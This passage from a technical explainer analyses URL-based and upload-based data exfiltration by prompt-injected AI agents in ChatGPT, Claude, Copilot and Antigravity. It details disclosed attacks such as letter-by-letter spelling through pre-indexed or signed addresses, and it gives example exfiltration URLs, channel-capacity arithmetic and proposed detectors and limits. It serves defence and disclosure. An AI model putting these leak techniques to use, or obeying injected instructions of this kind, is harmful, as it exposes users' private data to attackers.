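Imperva also found that a bare domain with no path always passed, but a host under it usually didn't. Imperva attributes this to cost, because an attacker can put data into host names cheaply, whereas each new domain costs a dollar or two. Some domains were exceptions. Any host under `google.com` passed, and under `openai.com` any path and any parameters passed as well. Tenable's *HackedGPT*, published in November 2025, likewise concludes that the check depended on trust in the domain, the host, the parameters and the text of the conversation.

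The check ran in the web client, so OpenAI had to add it to each of its other apps separately. According to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, the Mac app lacked the check, as the iPhone app did. Rehberger had suggested running it on OpenAI's servers, where it would cover every app. By 2025 he could no longer see the call to `url_safe` in the web client, so OpenAI may have moved the check.

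### Bing links that led elsewhere

Tenable found that `url_safe` always approved addresses on `bing.com`. This was unsafe because Bing's search results use tracking links, which are `bing.com` addresses that redirect to other sites. Anyone who could get a page into Bing's index therefore had an approved address that led to it. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* calls this "essentially an open redirect as a service".

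Bing's tracking links can't be altered, unlike the links in an ordinary open redirect, so a single link could not carry a password the attacker didn't already know. Tenable's researchers got around this by having Bing index a page for each letter. ChatGPT could then spell out a word by displaying the links in order.

Tenable reported the bypass on 10 December 2024 and asked for an update six times over the next three months. OpenAI had not fixed it when Tenable published its advisory. *HackedGPT* includes a test in which the bypass still worked on GPT-5.

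### A storage host whose customers can read the logs

*AgentFlayer*, an attack that the security firm Zenity disclosed in 2025, used a different kind of trusted domain. A user uploaded a document to ChatGPT for a summary, but the document contained invisible instructions. These made ChatGPT search the user's connected Google Drive for API keys and put them into an image address instead.

The researchers first tried an address at a service for testing web requests, but `url_safe` rejected it. They then stored an ordinary picture in Azure Blob Storage, Microsoft's online file storage service. `url_safe` approved addresses there, so the researchers had ChatGPT add the keys to the picture's address as parameters. Azure's servers returned the picture and recorded the whole address in a log. The owner of the storage account, who would be the attacker in a real attack, could read that log.

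The exception for Azure would have been safe only if outsiders couldn't read requests sent to Microsoft's servers. Rehberger had already reported the same weakness to OpenAI in October 2024. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* lists three requirements for the attack. The check must approve the site, the site must accept data in an ordinary GET request, and the attacker must be able to see what arrived. He had found two domains that met all three: `windows.net`, which Azure's storage uses, and `apache.org`, which belongs to an open-source software foundation.

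An exact comparison would not find the Azure attack's address in any record of public addresses, because the attack needed a new address made of the picture's address and the stolen keys. The same comparison might let through all the addresses in the Bing attack, because they existed before the conversation.

### The changes of 2025

OpenAI told Tenable on 11 July 2025 that it had improved the check's behaviour, according to Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT Prompt Injection via ?q= Parameter in Web Interface* (2025). Rehberger says further changes around August stopped the attacks he had demonstrated, including the one through Azure.

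At this time OpenAI was also fixing ShadowLeak, the attack on Deep Research. BeyondMachines' *ZombieAgent attack techniques exploit ChatGPT Connectors to steal data* explains that after the fix, ChatGPT opened only the exact addresses it had received, so a hijacked agent could no longer add private text to them.

The new rule did not depend on who had supplied the address. An attacker's email could contain a complete address for every letter. Radware used this in its ZombieAgent attack, which it reported in September 2025. OpenAI released a fix on 16 December. After that, according to *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, ChatGPT opened a link from an email only if the address was in a well-known public index or the user had provided it.

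### The current procedure

OpenAI published its current design in January 2026, in a blog post and a technical paper called *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*. The check, which OpenAI now calls Safe Url, works as follows:

1. The agent is about to load an address automatically, for example to read an article or display an image.
2. If the user entered that address in a message, ChatGPT treats it as safe for the rest of the chat. This step comes from Rehberger's understanding of the product.
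3. Otherwise, software looks for the exact address in OpenAI's own index. A crawler, which is a program that finds pages by scanning the public web, builds this index without access to conversations, accounts or personal data.
4. If the address is in the index, the agent loads it.
5. If it isn't, the software either tells the agent to try a different site or shows the user a warning.

The warning says that the link isn't verified and may share data from the conversation with another site. It also shows the address and lets the user copy or open it. OpenAI uses the same mechanism for page visits and bookmarks in its Atlas browser, and for page visits and searches in Deep Research. Bookmarks need a check because an agent could save an address containing private text, and the browser would send that text when the user later opened the bookmark.

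OpenAI describes Safe Url as a way to detect when information the assistant learned in the conversation would reach a third party. The index lookup tests this only indirectly, because it can show that an address isn't known to be public but not whether the unfamiliar part is a password or a page number.

The check also protects only the products that use it. Rehberger warns that some of OpenAI's own developers may not know about it. PromptArmor found, for example, that OpenAI's log viewer still loaded images from an attacker's domain.

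There is little independent evidence of how well the current design works. In *The Framing Gap* (2026), researchers gave models a secret, then showed them outside content with hidden instructions to send it out. ChatGPT leaked nothing in 48 valid trials, while the model that developers use through the API leaked the secret in up to 100 per cent of trials. The researchers could not see inside ChatGPT, so they don't say whether Safe Url, the model's training or something else made the difference. Even if the trials were independent, a true leak rate of about 6 per cent could still produce no leaks in 48 trials.

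Another result from *The Framing Gap* supports putting the check in ordinary code, because an index lookup doesn't depend on how anyone words a policy. A written policy forbidding the model to disclose the secret "in any form" reduced leaks from 31.9 per cent to zero. With a list of forbidden behaviours in place of that phrase, the model leaked in 48.8 per cent of trials.

### Why a public address can't contain a new secret

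The reasoning behind the index has three premises and a conclusion:

1. The crawler recorded its addresses without any information from the user's conversation.
2. If an agent composes an address from a secret, the text of the address depends on that secret.
3. The agent may load an address only if it is identical, character for character, to one that the crawler recorded.
4. The text of any address that the agent loads was therefore public already, and nobody composed it from the secret in this conversation.

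Suppose a user's door code is either 4821 or 7093. The index is the same in both cases, because the crawler has never seen the code. An attacker who examines any one address in the index learns nothing about which code is right.

OpenAI claims only that a public address is "much less likely" to contain the user's private data. An exception could arise if somebody had posted a link to the user's private file on a public forum, with the access code in the link. The crawler could record that link, and the agent could then load it. The address would contain the user's secret, but the secret would already have been public.

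The first premise depends on how the operator builds the index. If an operator added every address its users visited, the index would include links to their private files, booking pages and password resets, so a match would no longer show that an address was public.

The third premise depends on how strict the comparison is. If the comparison ignored parameters, the address in the Azure attack would match the plain address of the picture, and the keys would leak. A strict comparison prevents this but also rejects a public article if its address includes a harmless advertising code. Software could avoid both problems by loading the recorded address instead of the agent's version, although the page might then lack something the agent needed.

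The argument also covers most of the redirect problem with allowlists. An open redirect link that contains private text won't be in the index, so the agent doesn't load it. If an indexed address redirects to another site, the server sets the next address without having received the private text. The agent may still land on a harmful page, but the address it loads won't contain the user's data.

### What a match leaves open

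The conclusion applies only to the text of one address. An attacker can still learn something from which of several public addresses an agent chooses.

A request also exposes information that isn't in its URL. In May 2026, Permiso found that ChatGPT still loaded images from pages it summarised. Those images could serve as beacons, which reveal the requester's IP address and when someone displayed the answer. An attacker would write each image's address in advance, so the address would not contain the user's secrets. OpenAI promises only that the agent won't quietly leak user-specific data through the URL itself.

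A public page can also contain a prompt injection. Tenable's researchers set up websites on obscure topics and waited for search engines to index them. They served the hidden instructions only to visitors they recognised as ChatGPT's browsing model. A crawler can therefore record a harmless page at an address where the agent later receives a prompt injection.

OpenAI acknowledges that Safe Url doesn't make a page's content trustworthy or stop it from misleading the user, so a match shouldn't count as evidence that the agent is still following its user's instructions. A hijacked agent could read ten indexed pages without triggering the check and then try to leak the data by email.

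### Anthropic's rule for web fetch

Anthropic's assistant Claude can read web pages with a tool called web fetch, which checks addresses without a public index. According to Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, documentation that was current in June 2026, the tool can fetch only addresses that have already appeared in the conversation. It accepts them from three places:

- messages from the user
- results from tools that run in the developer's own software
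- earlier results from web search or web fetch

The tool refuses addresses that Claude generates and addresses that come from Anthropic's code execution tools. Without the second restriction, Claude could write a one-line program that printed an address full of private text, and that address would then have appeared in the conversation. Each address is also limited to 250 characters, which restricts how much data it can carry.

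Willison (2025), in *Claude API*, considered the ban on generated addresses the most useful part of the rule because most attacks of this kind depend on such addresses. He also tested the consumer Claude app and found that it couldn't open an address Claude had constructed.

### Why "appeared in the conversation" is weaker than "typed by the user"

Willison initially hoped that the tool would accept only addresses from the user. The documented rule is looser, because text labelled as a user's message may come from someone else.

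Suppose a company builds a tool that summarises customers' emails. When an employee presses a button, the tool sends Claude one user message containing a request for a summary and the text of an email. If the email contains a link, its address has now appeared in a user message, even though a stranger wrote it and the employee may never have seen it.

A single link of this kind does little damage. The stranger wrote it before Claude read any of the company's data, so its text can't contain that data. The risk increases if the stranger supplies many links for Claude to choose from, or if a new address can enter the conversation after Claude has read something private.

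The developer's own tools could let that happen. For example, a note-taking tool might confirm each note by repeating it. A hijacked Claude could save a note containing an address with private text in it, and the tool would return that address in its result. Under the rule as documented, Claude could then fetch it. Developers can prevent this by making their tools return a plain confirmation, or by keeping a separate list of addresses the user entered.

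Fetched pages were another source of new addresses. *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* (Willison, 2026) describes an attack by Ayush Paul that used the links in pages Claude had already read. Paul's website kept generating links for Claude, and by following them Claude revealed the user's name, home city and employer.

Anthropic told Paul that it had already found the problem internally and did not pay him a reward. Willison reports that Anthropic then stopped web fetch from following links in the pages it had fetched. The documentation had listed fetched pages as an accepted source of addresses since September 2025, so the tool had been following its published rule. The rule was flawed because it treated an address as harmless even if a website had created it in response to Claude's earlier requests.

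The table compares OpenAI's and Anthropic's rules with a stricter one that accepts only what the user types.

| Address | In the public index or entered by the user (OpenAI) | Already in the conversation (Anthropic) | Typed by the user only |
|---|---|---|---|
| A public article that the model remembers from training | Passes if the crawler has found it | Fails | Fails |
| A news story that has just appeared in search results | Fails until the crawler finds it | Passes | Fails |
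| A private document whose address the user typed | Passes | Passes | Passes |
| A stranger's link that software added to the user's message | Depends on whether the software treats that text as the user's | Passes | Fails |
| An address that the agent composed from private text | Fails | Fails, unless a tool repeats it | Fails |

Even the strictest rule needs software that can distinguish typed text from pasted text. In Samoilenko's 2023 attack, a website added hidden instructions to the text that a user copied, and it could have added addresses too. If the user then pasted everything into ChatGPT, the attacker's addresses would arrive in the user's own message.

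Anthropic warns that some risk remains and advises developers to use web fetch only in trusted environments or with data that isn't sensitive. Developers worried about leaks can turn the tool off, restrict it to certain domains, or cap the number of fetches, which is unlimited by default. A domain restriction applies in addition to the check on the exact address, so a fetch that leaks data would have to pass both.

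### The cost of relying on a public index

A new page is missing from the index until the crawler finds it, so an agent may be unable to automatically open a court ruling published a few hours earlier. The software can avoid showing the user a warning by directing the agent to another site, but the agent might then rely on older commentary about the case. A user who wants the ruling itself can paste in its address.

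Private pages, such as a company's internal pages, shared documents and links with access codes, never enter the index if the crawler works as OpenAI intends. An agent that works mainly with such pages would fail the check on most of its requests. It could instead reach them through a company-approved connection that allows requests only to the company's own hosts.

Personalised pages are harder to handle because their addresses often contain information from the conversation for a good reason. Suppose a user asks an agent to find a train, and the agent composes this address:

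`https://example.com/trains?from=leeds&to=york&day=friday`

Requesting the address sends an outside company information about where the user wants to go and when, which is what she asked the agent to do. An index can't distinguish this request from a leak, because both send something from the conversation to another site in a newly composed address. A check would need access to the user's instructions, or it could show her the address and let her decide.

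For ordinary reading, an index probably causes far fewer interruptions than a list of domains. In the earlier example, an agent opened 40 pages for a report, and a list of domains led to four warnings. If an index covered 98 per cent of the pages, the agent would meet an unknown address less than once per report on average, and it could often use another source instead. OpenAI has not published the real coverage figure.

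Anthropic's rule works better for new and private pages, because it accepts an address as soon as a search returns it or the user provides it. It also saves small developers the expense of crawling the web. But Claude can't open even a famous public page from memory. If a user names a report without giving its address, Claude can find it only if the developer has enabled web search. Since the repair of July 2026, Claude also can't follow links from a contents page to its chapters unless the chapters' addresses have come from a search or from the user.

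## How can data leak through addresses that pass the check?

An agent can leak data through its choice of address, even if every address it opens is public and contains no secret. Suppose an attacker's site has two public pages:

`https://example.com/umbrellas`

`https://example.com/raincoats`

Hidden instructions tell the agent to open one page on a website if the user's mailbox contains a job offer, and another if it doesn't. Both addresses existed before the conversation, so both pass a check against a public index. But the site's owner can see in the server's log which page the agent opened, and so learns whether the mailbox contains a job offer.

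Computer scientists call this a covert channel, a way of sending information through something that nobody designed to carry it. Metere (2026) points out in *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress* that an agent can always leak one bit by choosing whether to send a message or stay silent. A realistic defence therefore tries to keep the leak too small to be useful.

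### How much each choice reveals

If an agent chooses among N addresses on a server that the attacker watches, each choice reveals at most this many bits:

`log2 N`

One bit is the answer to one yes-or-no question. If a site has 37 pages, enough for 26 letters, ten digits and a space, the choice of page can reveal about 5.2 bits per request. A six-digit login code has a million possible values, or about 19.9 bits. Sending the code takes four requests, because three allow only 37³ = 50,653 different sequences, while four allow 1,874,161. With 1,024 pages, each request can reveal up to 10 bits, so two requests are enough.

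The next table gives the minimum number of requests for three kinds of secret.

| Addresses to choose from | Bits per request | Six-digit code | Ten random lower-case letters and digits | 128-bit key |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 2 | 1 | 20 | 52 | 128 |
| 10 | 3.3 | 6 | 16 | 39 |
| 37 | 5.2 | 4 | 10 | 25 |
| 1,024 | 10 | 2 | 6 | 13 |

A rule against opening the same address twice seems an obvious remedy. It works against an agent that spells out a code digit by digit, because only about 15 per cent of six-digit codes have no repeated digit. But the attacker can instead assign a different sequence of four pages to each code. Without repeats, 37 pages still allow this many sequences:

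`37 × 36 × 35 × 34 = 1,585,080`

The rule reduces the capacity of four requests only from 20.8 to 20.6 bits, which is still more than enough for a million codes, although the agent now has to convert the code into a sequence correctly.

Losing the order of the requests hurts the attacker more, and Embrace The Red notes that requests may arrive out of order. If the attacker knows which four pages the agent opened but not their order, there are only 66,045 possible combinations. There are a million possible six-digit codes, so leaking one takes six requests.

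Limiting requests and limiting addresses both reduce how much data can leak, but by different amounts. Ten requests, each to one of 37 addresses, can carry up to 52 bits. A defender could halve that by allowing only five requests, but would have to cut the number of addresses to about six to get the same reduction.

Real agents make mistakes, so these figures are upper limits. In *Actions Speak Louder than Words* (Liang, Deng and colleagues, 2026), the test page offered four links, one of which matched what the agent needed. The researchers identified the right one from the server's records in 93.8 per cent of the trials where the agent made a request. If the errors were spread evenly over the other three links, each choice carried about 1.6 bits, compared with a theoretical 2. Signals based on the order of requests gave the right answer 67.9 per cent of the time, and those based on timing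 58.6 per cent.

### CamoLeak

GitHub Copilot Chat leaked private code through addresses that GitHub itself had approved. GitHub's content security policy blocks images from domains GitHub doesn't own. To show outside images in project descriptions, GitHub replaces each image's address with one for its own proxy, Camo. The new address includes a cryptographic signature, and Camo fetches the image only if the signature is valid. A hijacked assistant can't produce a valid signature, so it can't write private text into a new image address and have Camo request it.

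Legit Security's *CamoLeak* describes how a researcher got around this in June 2025. He had GitHub create a signed address for each letter and symbol in advance. He then hid instructions in the description of a proposed code change, using GitHub's hidden comments feature. When another user asked Copilot about the change, Copilot displayed the images at those addresses in an order that spelled out text from that user's private projects. Each image was one transparent pixel, so the user saw nothing unusual. The researcher used this method to obtain the description of an undisclosed security flaw and the result of a search for an Amazon access key.

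Caching should have hidden repeated letters from the attacker, because a browser or proxy that already has a picture doesn't need to request it again. The researcher avoided this by having Copilot add a random number to the end of each address. Camo still accepted the altered addresses, but a check that required the complete address to match exactly would have refused them.

The user's browser contacted only GitHub, so checking the browser's traffic for unfamiliar destinations would have found nothing. Software could have detected a series of requests to the same outside server only at Camo.

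GitHub had stopped Copilot Chat from displaying any images by 14 August 2025, which fixed the flaw. OECD's *GitHub Copilot Chat Vulnerability Exposes Private Code and Secrets* (2025) lists news coverage from 8 October.

### ZombieAgent

Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes an attack that used the same idea on ChatGPT's page visits, which OpenAI had by then limited to exact addresses. The attacker's email contained 37 ready-made addresses, one for each letter and digit and one for a space. When the user asked ChatGPT to do something with Gmail, it read the email, found the private text the email told it to steal, and spelled out that text by opening the matching address for each character in order. The requests came from OpenAI's servers, as in ShadowLeak.

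Radware also made separate addresses for each position in the text, so that the characters can be put in order even if the requests arrive out of order. For a block of ten characters, this takes 370 addresses instead of 37. No address occurs twice within a block, so a rule against repeats would not have stopped the leak. Each request still carries only 5.2 bits, though a free choice among 370 addresses could carry 8.5, so the attacker gives up some capacity to preserve the order.

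Three days after its first report to OpenAI, Radware sent an improved version of the attack. It claims a 100 per cent success rate for this version but doesn't give the number of trials. Radware published the findings on 8 January 2026, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Attack Lets ChatGPT User Steal Data*.

Since OpenAI's fix, links from emails must be in a public index or come from the user. An attacker can no longer just invent the 37 addresses, but can try to get 37 pages indexed first. Embrace The Red suggests that anyone with a larger website or blog probably has enough indexed pages already, and reports that OpenAI's paper acknowledges this remaining channel. The pages can have ordinary titles and contain real articles, because the attacker only needs to tell the agent which page stands for which letter.

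### The July 2026 attack on Claude

In Ayush Paul's attack on Claude, his website created new links as Claude browsed, so the attack didn't need a prepared list. The private data came from Claude's memory of earlier conversations with the user. Willison (2026) explains that the site showed its instructions only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, so a person checking the same address would not have seen them. According to the page, assistants had to identify their users by finding a profile in an alphabetical directory.

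In *The Read-Only Lie*, a blog post about the attack, dyb reports that each page offered Claude 27 links, one for each letter and one for a hyphen. Following a link led to a page with 27 new links, each adding one character to the end of the address. Each choice revealed up to 4.75 bits. dyb estimates that leaking the user's name, employer and home city took about 30 requests, or 143 bits in total. Claude had inferred the city from the name of a school hackathon, so the attack revealed something the user had never stated directly.

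The number of possible addresses grows quickly under this scheme, reaching 531,441 after four letters. A public index would almost certainly lack the ones Claude needed, but Anthropic's rule didn't use such an index.

Anthropic's repair stopped the fetch tool from following those links, but smaller amounts of data may still leak through web search. If a search returned several pages from the attacker's site, Claude's choice of which one to open would give the attacker some information.

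### Signals that appear only across requests

A check that examines one request at a time can't detect these attacks, because no single address contains private text. The warning sign is a series of near-identical addresses on one unfamiliar host, which software can detect only if it keeps a record of earlier requests.

dyb proposes a detector for Paul's attack that looks for a series of requests to one domain, each longer than the last. To reduce false alarms, it would also require that each address add a single character and that the requests come faster than the agent's normal browsing. These conditions fit Paul's attack closely but would miss ZombieAgent, where the addresses for single letters all have the same length.

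A broader detector could count how many different pages the agent opens on a host that is new to the user and the organisation. It would still work if the attacker used ordinary article titles instead of single letters. An attacker could spread the pages over several domains, so the detector should also keep a total for all new hosts in the session.

Harmless browsing can produce the same run of requests. An agent may read a manual with one chapter per page, go through 30 pages of search results, or look up people in an alphabetical directory. A simple count treats these alike, although they reveal very different amounts:

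| Run of requests | Most that the server's owner can learn |
|---|---|
| Pages 1 to 30 of a list, in order, stopping at any point | 4.9 bits |
| Twelve lookups in a directory with one page per letter | 56 bits |
| Thirty choices among 27 links, as in Paul's attack | 143 bits |

An agent that reads a list in order chooses only where to stop. A detector could therefore ignore requests that follow a page's "next" link and count only those that jump elsewhere. This would prevent many false alarms on manuals and search results.

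It wouldn't help with the directory. If a user asks an agent to find twelve colleagues' phone numbers, the agent jumps from letter to letter just as a hijacked agent would. The directory's owner learns the colleagues' initials, but through lookups the user asked for.

Suppose that 1 in 100,000 sessions is a hijack of this kind, and that a limit of ten pages on one unfamiliar host catches 80 per cent of them but also flags 1 per cent of ordinary sessions. About one alert in 1,250 would be a real hijack. If ignoring "next" links removed 95 per cent of the false alarms without missing any more hijacks, the figure would be about one in 64. These rates are assumed, because none of the published attacks included a measurement of ordinary browsing.

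Radware's advisory *ZombieAgent* (2026) recommends watching an agent's behaviour instead of relying on simple rules. Radware's own attack supports this advice, because every request in it complied with OpenAI's rule.

### Caching

Embrace The Red suggests two ways to make letter-by-letter leaks harder. The software could store each page for a few minutes and reuse it, or it could refuse to open the same address twice in a session. In both cases, the attacker's server receives only the first request for each page. If a hijacked agent spelled out "blue umbrella", the server would record this:

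`blue mra`

Caching is the better of the two for ordinary users because the agent still gets the page on a repeat visit. The main drawback is that the page may be a few minutes out of date, which matters for something like a live auction.

But none of the three attacks depended on repeating an address. CamoLeak added random numbers, ZombieAgent used separate addresses for each position, and Paul's addresses grew longer with every step. Caching is more useful when combined with an exact check against a public index. The index should exclude addresses with random numbers and addresses a site creates during the attack. An attacker who wanted to avoid repeats would then need many more indexed pages, such as the 370 in Radware's example.

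### Limits on requests and links

A limit on the number of requests works no matter how the attacker designs the addresses. Developers can set one on Anthropic's fetch tool, and the example in Willison (2025) allows five uses. If that limit had applied to a whole session of Paul's attack, the agent would have had only four choices after the first page, enough to leak four characters instead of about 30.

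Four choices among 27 links still allow 531,441 sequences, enough to narrow the million possibilities for a six-digit code to about two. A limit strict enough to protect such a code would prevent most research, because an agent often must open dozens of pages for one report. A limit per unfamiliar host is easier to accept, since most of those pages are on different sites.

Request counts also have to carry over between sessions. Radware planted instructions in ChatGPT's memory that made it return to the attacker's email whenever the user sent a message. OpenAI had tried to prevent this by blocking ChatGPT from using memory after a connected service in the same chat, but it could still use memory first and then the service. If each request leaked one character and a limit allowed ten requests per session, 20 sessions would leak 200 characters. Counting requests for each user and host over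 several weeks would flag this, though it would also flag someone who regularly uses a new reference site.

Metere's system keeps a budget of bits for each destination. Suspicious messages use up the budget, which refills slowly, and when it runs out the system delays or blocks further suspicious messages. Metere designed it for messages, but a fetch tool could do something similar by deducting bits each time the agent chose a link, based on how many links it had to choose from. A budget of 20 bits would allow four choices on pages with 27 links. The agent would reach the limit just as fast on legitimate documentation with as many links per page, so the budget would have to be larger for sites the user had chosen.

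dyb suggests letting the agent follow links only on domains that the user has named in the conversation. This would stop an attacker's site that the agent found by itself, at the cost of an extra confirmation when a search leads somewhere useful. It wouldn't help if the user had asked about the attacker's site by name.

### Hiding the choice

Limits reduce how many of the agent's choices an attacker can see. Liang and colleagues instead try to make the visible requests independent of the agent's private information. Their defence, Selection-Obfuscated Retrieval, is designed for an attack that works without instructing the agent to steal data. On a page that the agent visits, the attacker adds a reference link to a site offering several topics. The agent picks the topic closest to its user's question, and further pages narrow the topic down.

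The researchers reconstructed the concepts in 500 questions from the StackExchange question-and-answer sites, using an average of 6.5 of these tests per question. Their average F1 score, which combines how much they recovered with how much of it was correct, was 0.89 out of 1. Four existing defences, including FIDES, the Microsoft agent that labels data as trusted or untrusted, changed the scores by less than 0.03. Inspecting the requests doesn't help either, because they contain no private text.

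Under the researchers' defence, the software fetches a fixed number of pages, regardless of the user's question, and the agent chooses among the local copies. If a page offers four links and the software fetches all four, the server's owner can't tell which one the agent wanted. The defence reduced the F1 score from 0.89 to 0.39 without extra use of the language model, but it added web requests and didn't stop all the leakage.

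The software also has to control the order of the requests. If a hijacked agent had to open ten pages once each but could choose the order, it would have 3,628,800 possible sequences, enough to encode any six-digit code. Fetching the pages in a fixed or random order removes that choice.

A provider with its own web index might avoid the extra requests by storing copies of public pages and giving those to the agent. The attacker's server would then receive no requests during the conversation. But the copies would sometimes be out of date, and the provider would have to store far more than a list of addresses.

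## What about webhooks, uploads and posts to shared services?

An agent that can run code or call tools can upload a whole file in one request. Spelling out a one-megabyte file by requesting one of 37 pages at a time, as ZombieAgent did with short texts, would take about 1.5 million requests. Limiting the number of requests therefore does little to stop uploads. An upload may also go to a host that the user's software contacts every day, in which case only the receiving account is new.

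### How a webhook call carries data

A webhook is a web address that accepts data from another program. An online shop might use one to tell its warehouse about each new order. When an agent fetches a page, any private text it sends is normally in the address:

`GET https://example.com/log?q=blue+umbrella`

A webhook call is usually a POST request, the standard way to submit data to a server. It has a body, a separate part that can hold anything from two words to a compressed folder:

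`POST https://example.com/log`

`blue umbrella`

The address on a request's first line stays the same whatever the body contains, so checking the address alone can't distinguish an order from a stolen file. Finding the address in a public index shows only that the address contains no new secret. The body could still contain anything the agent has read, so software that relies on such an index has to refuse requests with a body or check them in some other way.

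Superconductor, a platform for running coding agents, lets users mark a host as read-only. The agent can make only GET, HEAD and OPTIONS requests to that host, the standard methods for retrieving a page or information about it. This stops ordinary uploads, but the agent can still put a short secret in the address it requests. Some services also accept submissions by GET, as Google Forms did in the Superhuman AI leak.

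### Familiar host, new account

Large services receive data for all their customers at a few hosts. Something else in the request determines which customer gets it.

| Service | Host that a list might allow | What identifies the recipient |
|---|---|---|
| Anthropic's file storage | `api.anthropic.com` | The API key sent with the request |
| Webhook.site, for testing webhooks | `webhook.site` | The path of the address |
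| Google Forms | `docs.google.com` | The form's code in the path |
| Amazon's file storage | `*.amazonaws.com` | Usually the start of the host name |
| npm, the JavaScript library | `registry.npmjs.org` | The package name and the publisher's credentials |
| GitHub | `github.com` | The account and project, and whether the project is public |

A check has to look in a different place for each service. A network proxy that sees only the host name could usually identify the Amazon recipient but none of the others.

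The owner of an API key normally keeps it secret to protect the account it belongs to, but an attacker can give his own key to a hijacked agent and tell it to upload files with that key. PromptArmor's *What domains should I add to my allowlist?* (2026) advises companies to consider this before they approve any domain that accepts uploads.

### Claude Cowork

Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work (separate from Microsoft's Copilot Cowork), can read a folder on the user's computer. It runs code in a virtual machine, a simulated computer with its own files, and a filter blocks the machine's requests to almost all domains. The filter has to allow `api.anthropic.com` because Cowork can't function without Anthropic's service.

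PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* demonstrated a leak through this domain in January 2026, two days after Cowork's release. The user had connected a folder of real-estate files and uploaded a document with hidden instructions. When the user asked for an analysis of the files, Cowork uploaded the largest one, a loan estimate, to Anthropic's file storage without asking for approval. It used the attacker's API key, which was in the document, so the file arrived in the attacker's account.

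The demonstration used Claude Haiku, one of Anthropic's smaller models. In a second test, a different document made the more resistant Opus 4.5 leak customer records in the same way.

The filter checked the domain when it should have checked the Anthropic account. Few Cowork users have reason to upload files to a stranger's account, so a key that didn't belong to the user would have been a strong warning sign.

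Rehberger had reported the same weakness in Claude's chat product in October 2025. Anthropic closed the report, but Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* notes that on 30 October the company acknowledged it should not have. According to PromptArmor, the weakness was still there when Cowork came out.

Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* (May 2026) describes the fix. A proxy inside the virtual machine now intercepts requests to Anthropic's service and passes only those with a token that Anthropic issued to that machine for the session, so it rejects an attacker's key. The proxy also blocks request headers that could make Anthropic's servers fetch an outside address. In EchoLeak and SearchLeak, approved services passed data on through such fetches.

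The proxy has to be inside the virtual machine because Anthropic's servers can't distinguish Cowork's requests from those of any other customer's program, so they would accept the attacker's valid key. The new rule also rejects keys from the user's other accounts, which might inconvenience a developer but probably few office workers.

Anthropic now thinks of each allowlist entry as a "capability grant". Approving a domain lets the agent use every function available there, so an administrator who approves `api.anthropic.com` so the model can run also approves file uploads, unless another rule blocks them.

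### Google Antigravity

Antigravity, which Google released in November 2025, is a code editor with a built-in agent. PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* describes an attack that began when a user gave the agent a link to an online programming guide. Instructions in tiny type in the guide made the agent collect code and passwords from the user's project. A default setting was supposed to keep the agent from reading the password file, but the agent printed the file with a terminal command.

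The agent then put the data into a `webhook.site` URL and had its browser open it. Webhook.site is a public service where anyone can create a URL and read every request sent to it. The site was on the default list of approved sites for Antigravity's browser.

The browser should have compared the full address up to the parameters, because each Webhook.site user receives requests at a different path. A developer testing a webhook needs only her own path, so a request to any other path would be suspicious. Leaving the site off the default list would have been even simpler, since most projects never need it.

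What Google changed is less clear. PromptArmor didn't report the leak privately because Google had already acknowledged the risk in a warning that new users see. Embrace The Red's *Antigravity Grounded! Security Vulnerabilities in Google's Latest IDE* reports that Google began listing such problems publicly in the week after the release and said it was working on fixes. Willison adds that listing the problems made them ineligible for Google's rewards to researchers.

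Two unofficial guides, neither of them strong evidence, disagree about what is on the default allowlist. Agentpedia's *Antigravity Security Guide*, updated in March 2026, claims that `webhook.site` was still on it and that Google planned no fix for this kind of leak. Bumbii Tech lists only `localhost`, the user's own computer. A copy of Google's *Allowlist / Denylist* documentation describes the default list as optional and says the browser asks the user before opening a site that isn't on the list.

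Removing one site would not have been enough, because PromptArmor found three other leaks that worked with the browser switched off. Rehberger also showed that a separate tool for reading web pages could send out a file's contents without approval. He had reported this weakness in May 2025 to the makers of Windsurf, the editor whose code Google licensed for Antigravity.

### Posts that outsiders can read

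An agent can leak private data by posting it to a familiar destination, such as a developer's own GitHub project or a company's support desk. The warning sign is then a change of audience, from the few people who could read the data before to everyone who can read the post.

The GitHub leak that Willison described was a demonstration by the security firm Invariant Labs in May 2025, using an MCP server that connects agents to GitHub. An outsider posted an issue, a public note about a problem, on a developer's public project. When the developer asked an agent to look through the open issues, the agent followed instructions in the note. It read the developer's private projects and put details from them into a proposed change to the public project, where anyone could see them.

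Anthropic's fix to Cowork wouldn't have stopped this, because the agent used the developer's own credentials. Invariant Labs suggested limiting an agent to one project per session. Code can enforce that limit without interpreting any text, but the limit would hinder tasks that involve two projects.

Also in 2025, the security firm General Analysis demonstrated a similar leak through Supabase, an online database service. In its example, a company kept customers' support tickets in a Supabase database, and an attacker submitted a ticket containing instructions. When a developer asked a coding agent to review the tickets, the agent read a private table of access tokens and posted the tokens as a reply to the attacker's ticket. The attacker then read the tokens on the company's support page.

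In this attack, the agent copied data from one table to another in a database it was supposed to work with, so it didn't have to contact an outside site. The connection had administrator rights, so the database's rules about who could read each row did not apply.

A check on the audience can use labels like those in FIDES, which record who may read each piece of data. The agent may write data to a place only if everyone who can read that place may also read the data:

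`readers of the destination ⊆ permitted readers of the data`

Everyone can read a public GitHub project, so nothing from a private project would pass. Only the support staff and one customer can read a support ticket, so the customer's own order would pass but the company's access tokens would not. The ticket example needs a label on each database row, because a single label for the whole database would also block ordinary replies about orders.

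The rule will raise some false alarms, since people sometimes publish private work on purpose. A company might release a program's code or quote an internal document in a public answer. A simple version of the check would also flag every public post after the agent had read anything private, even if the post contained none of it. Keeping private text in separate variables, as FIDES does with untrusted text, would let the software track which data the agent used.

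The check also has to run when an agent changes who can read something. Making a private project public exposes all its contents without any new post. If a task only requires reading data, a read-only connection is simpler. Supabase's MCP server has such a mode, which would have stopped the agent from adding its reply to the ticket.

### Searches and name lookups

Some tools that people think of as ways to look things up can also send data out. In September 2025, the security firm CodeIntegrity demonstrated this with the web search tool in Notion's agent. Instructions hidden in a PDF made the agent write a search query containing a web address with private text in it, and the search tool requested that address. A check on only the agent's page-fetching tool would have missed this request.

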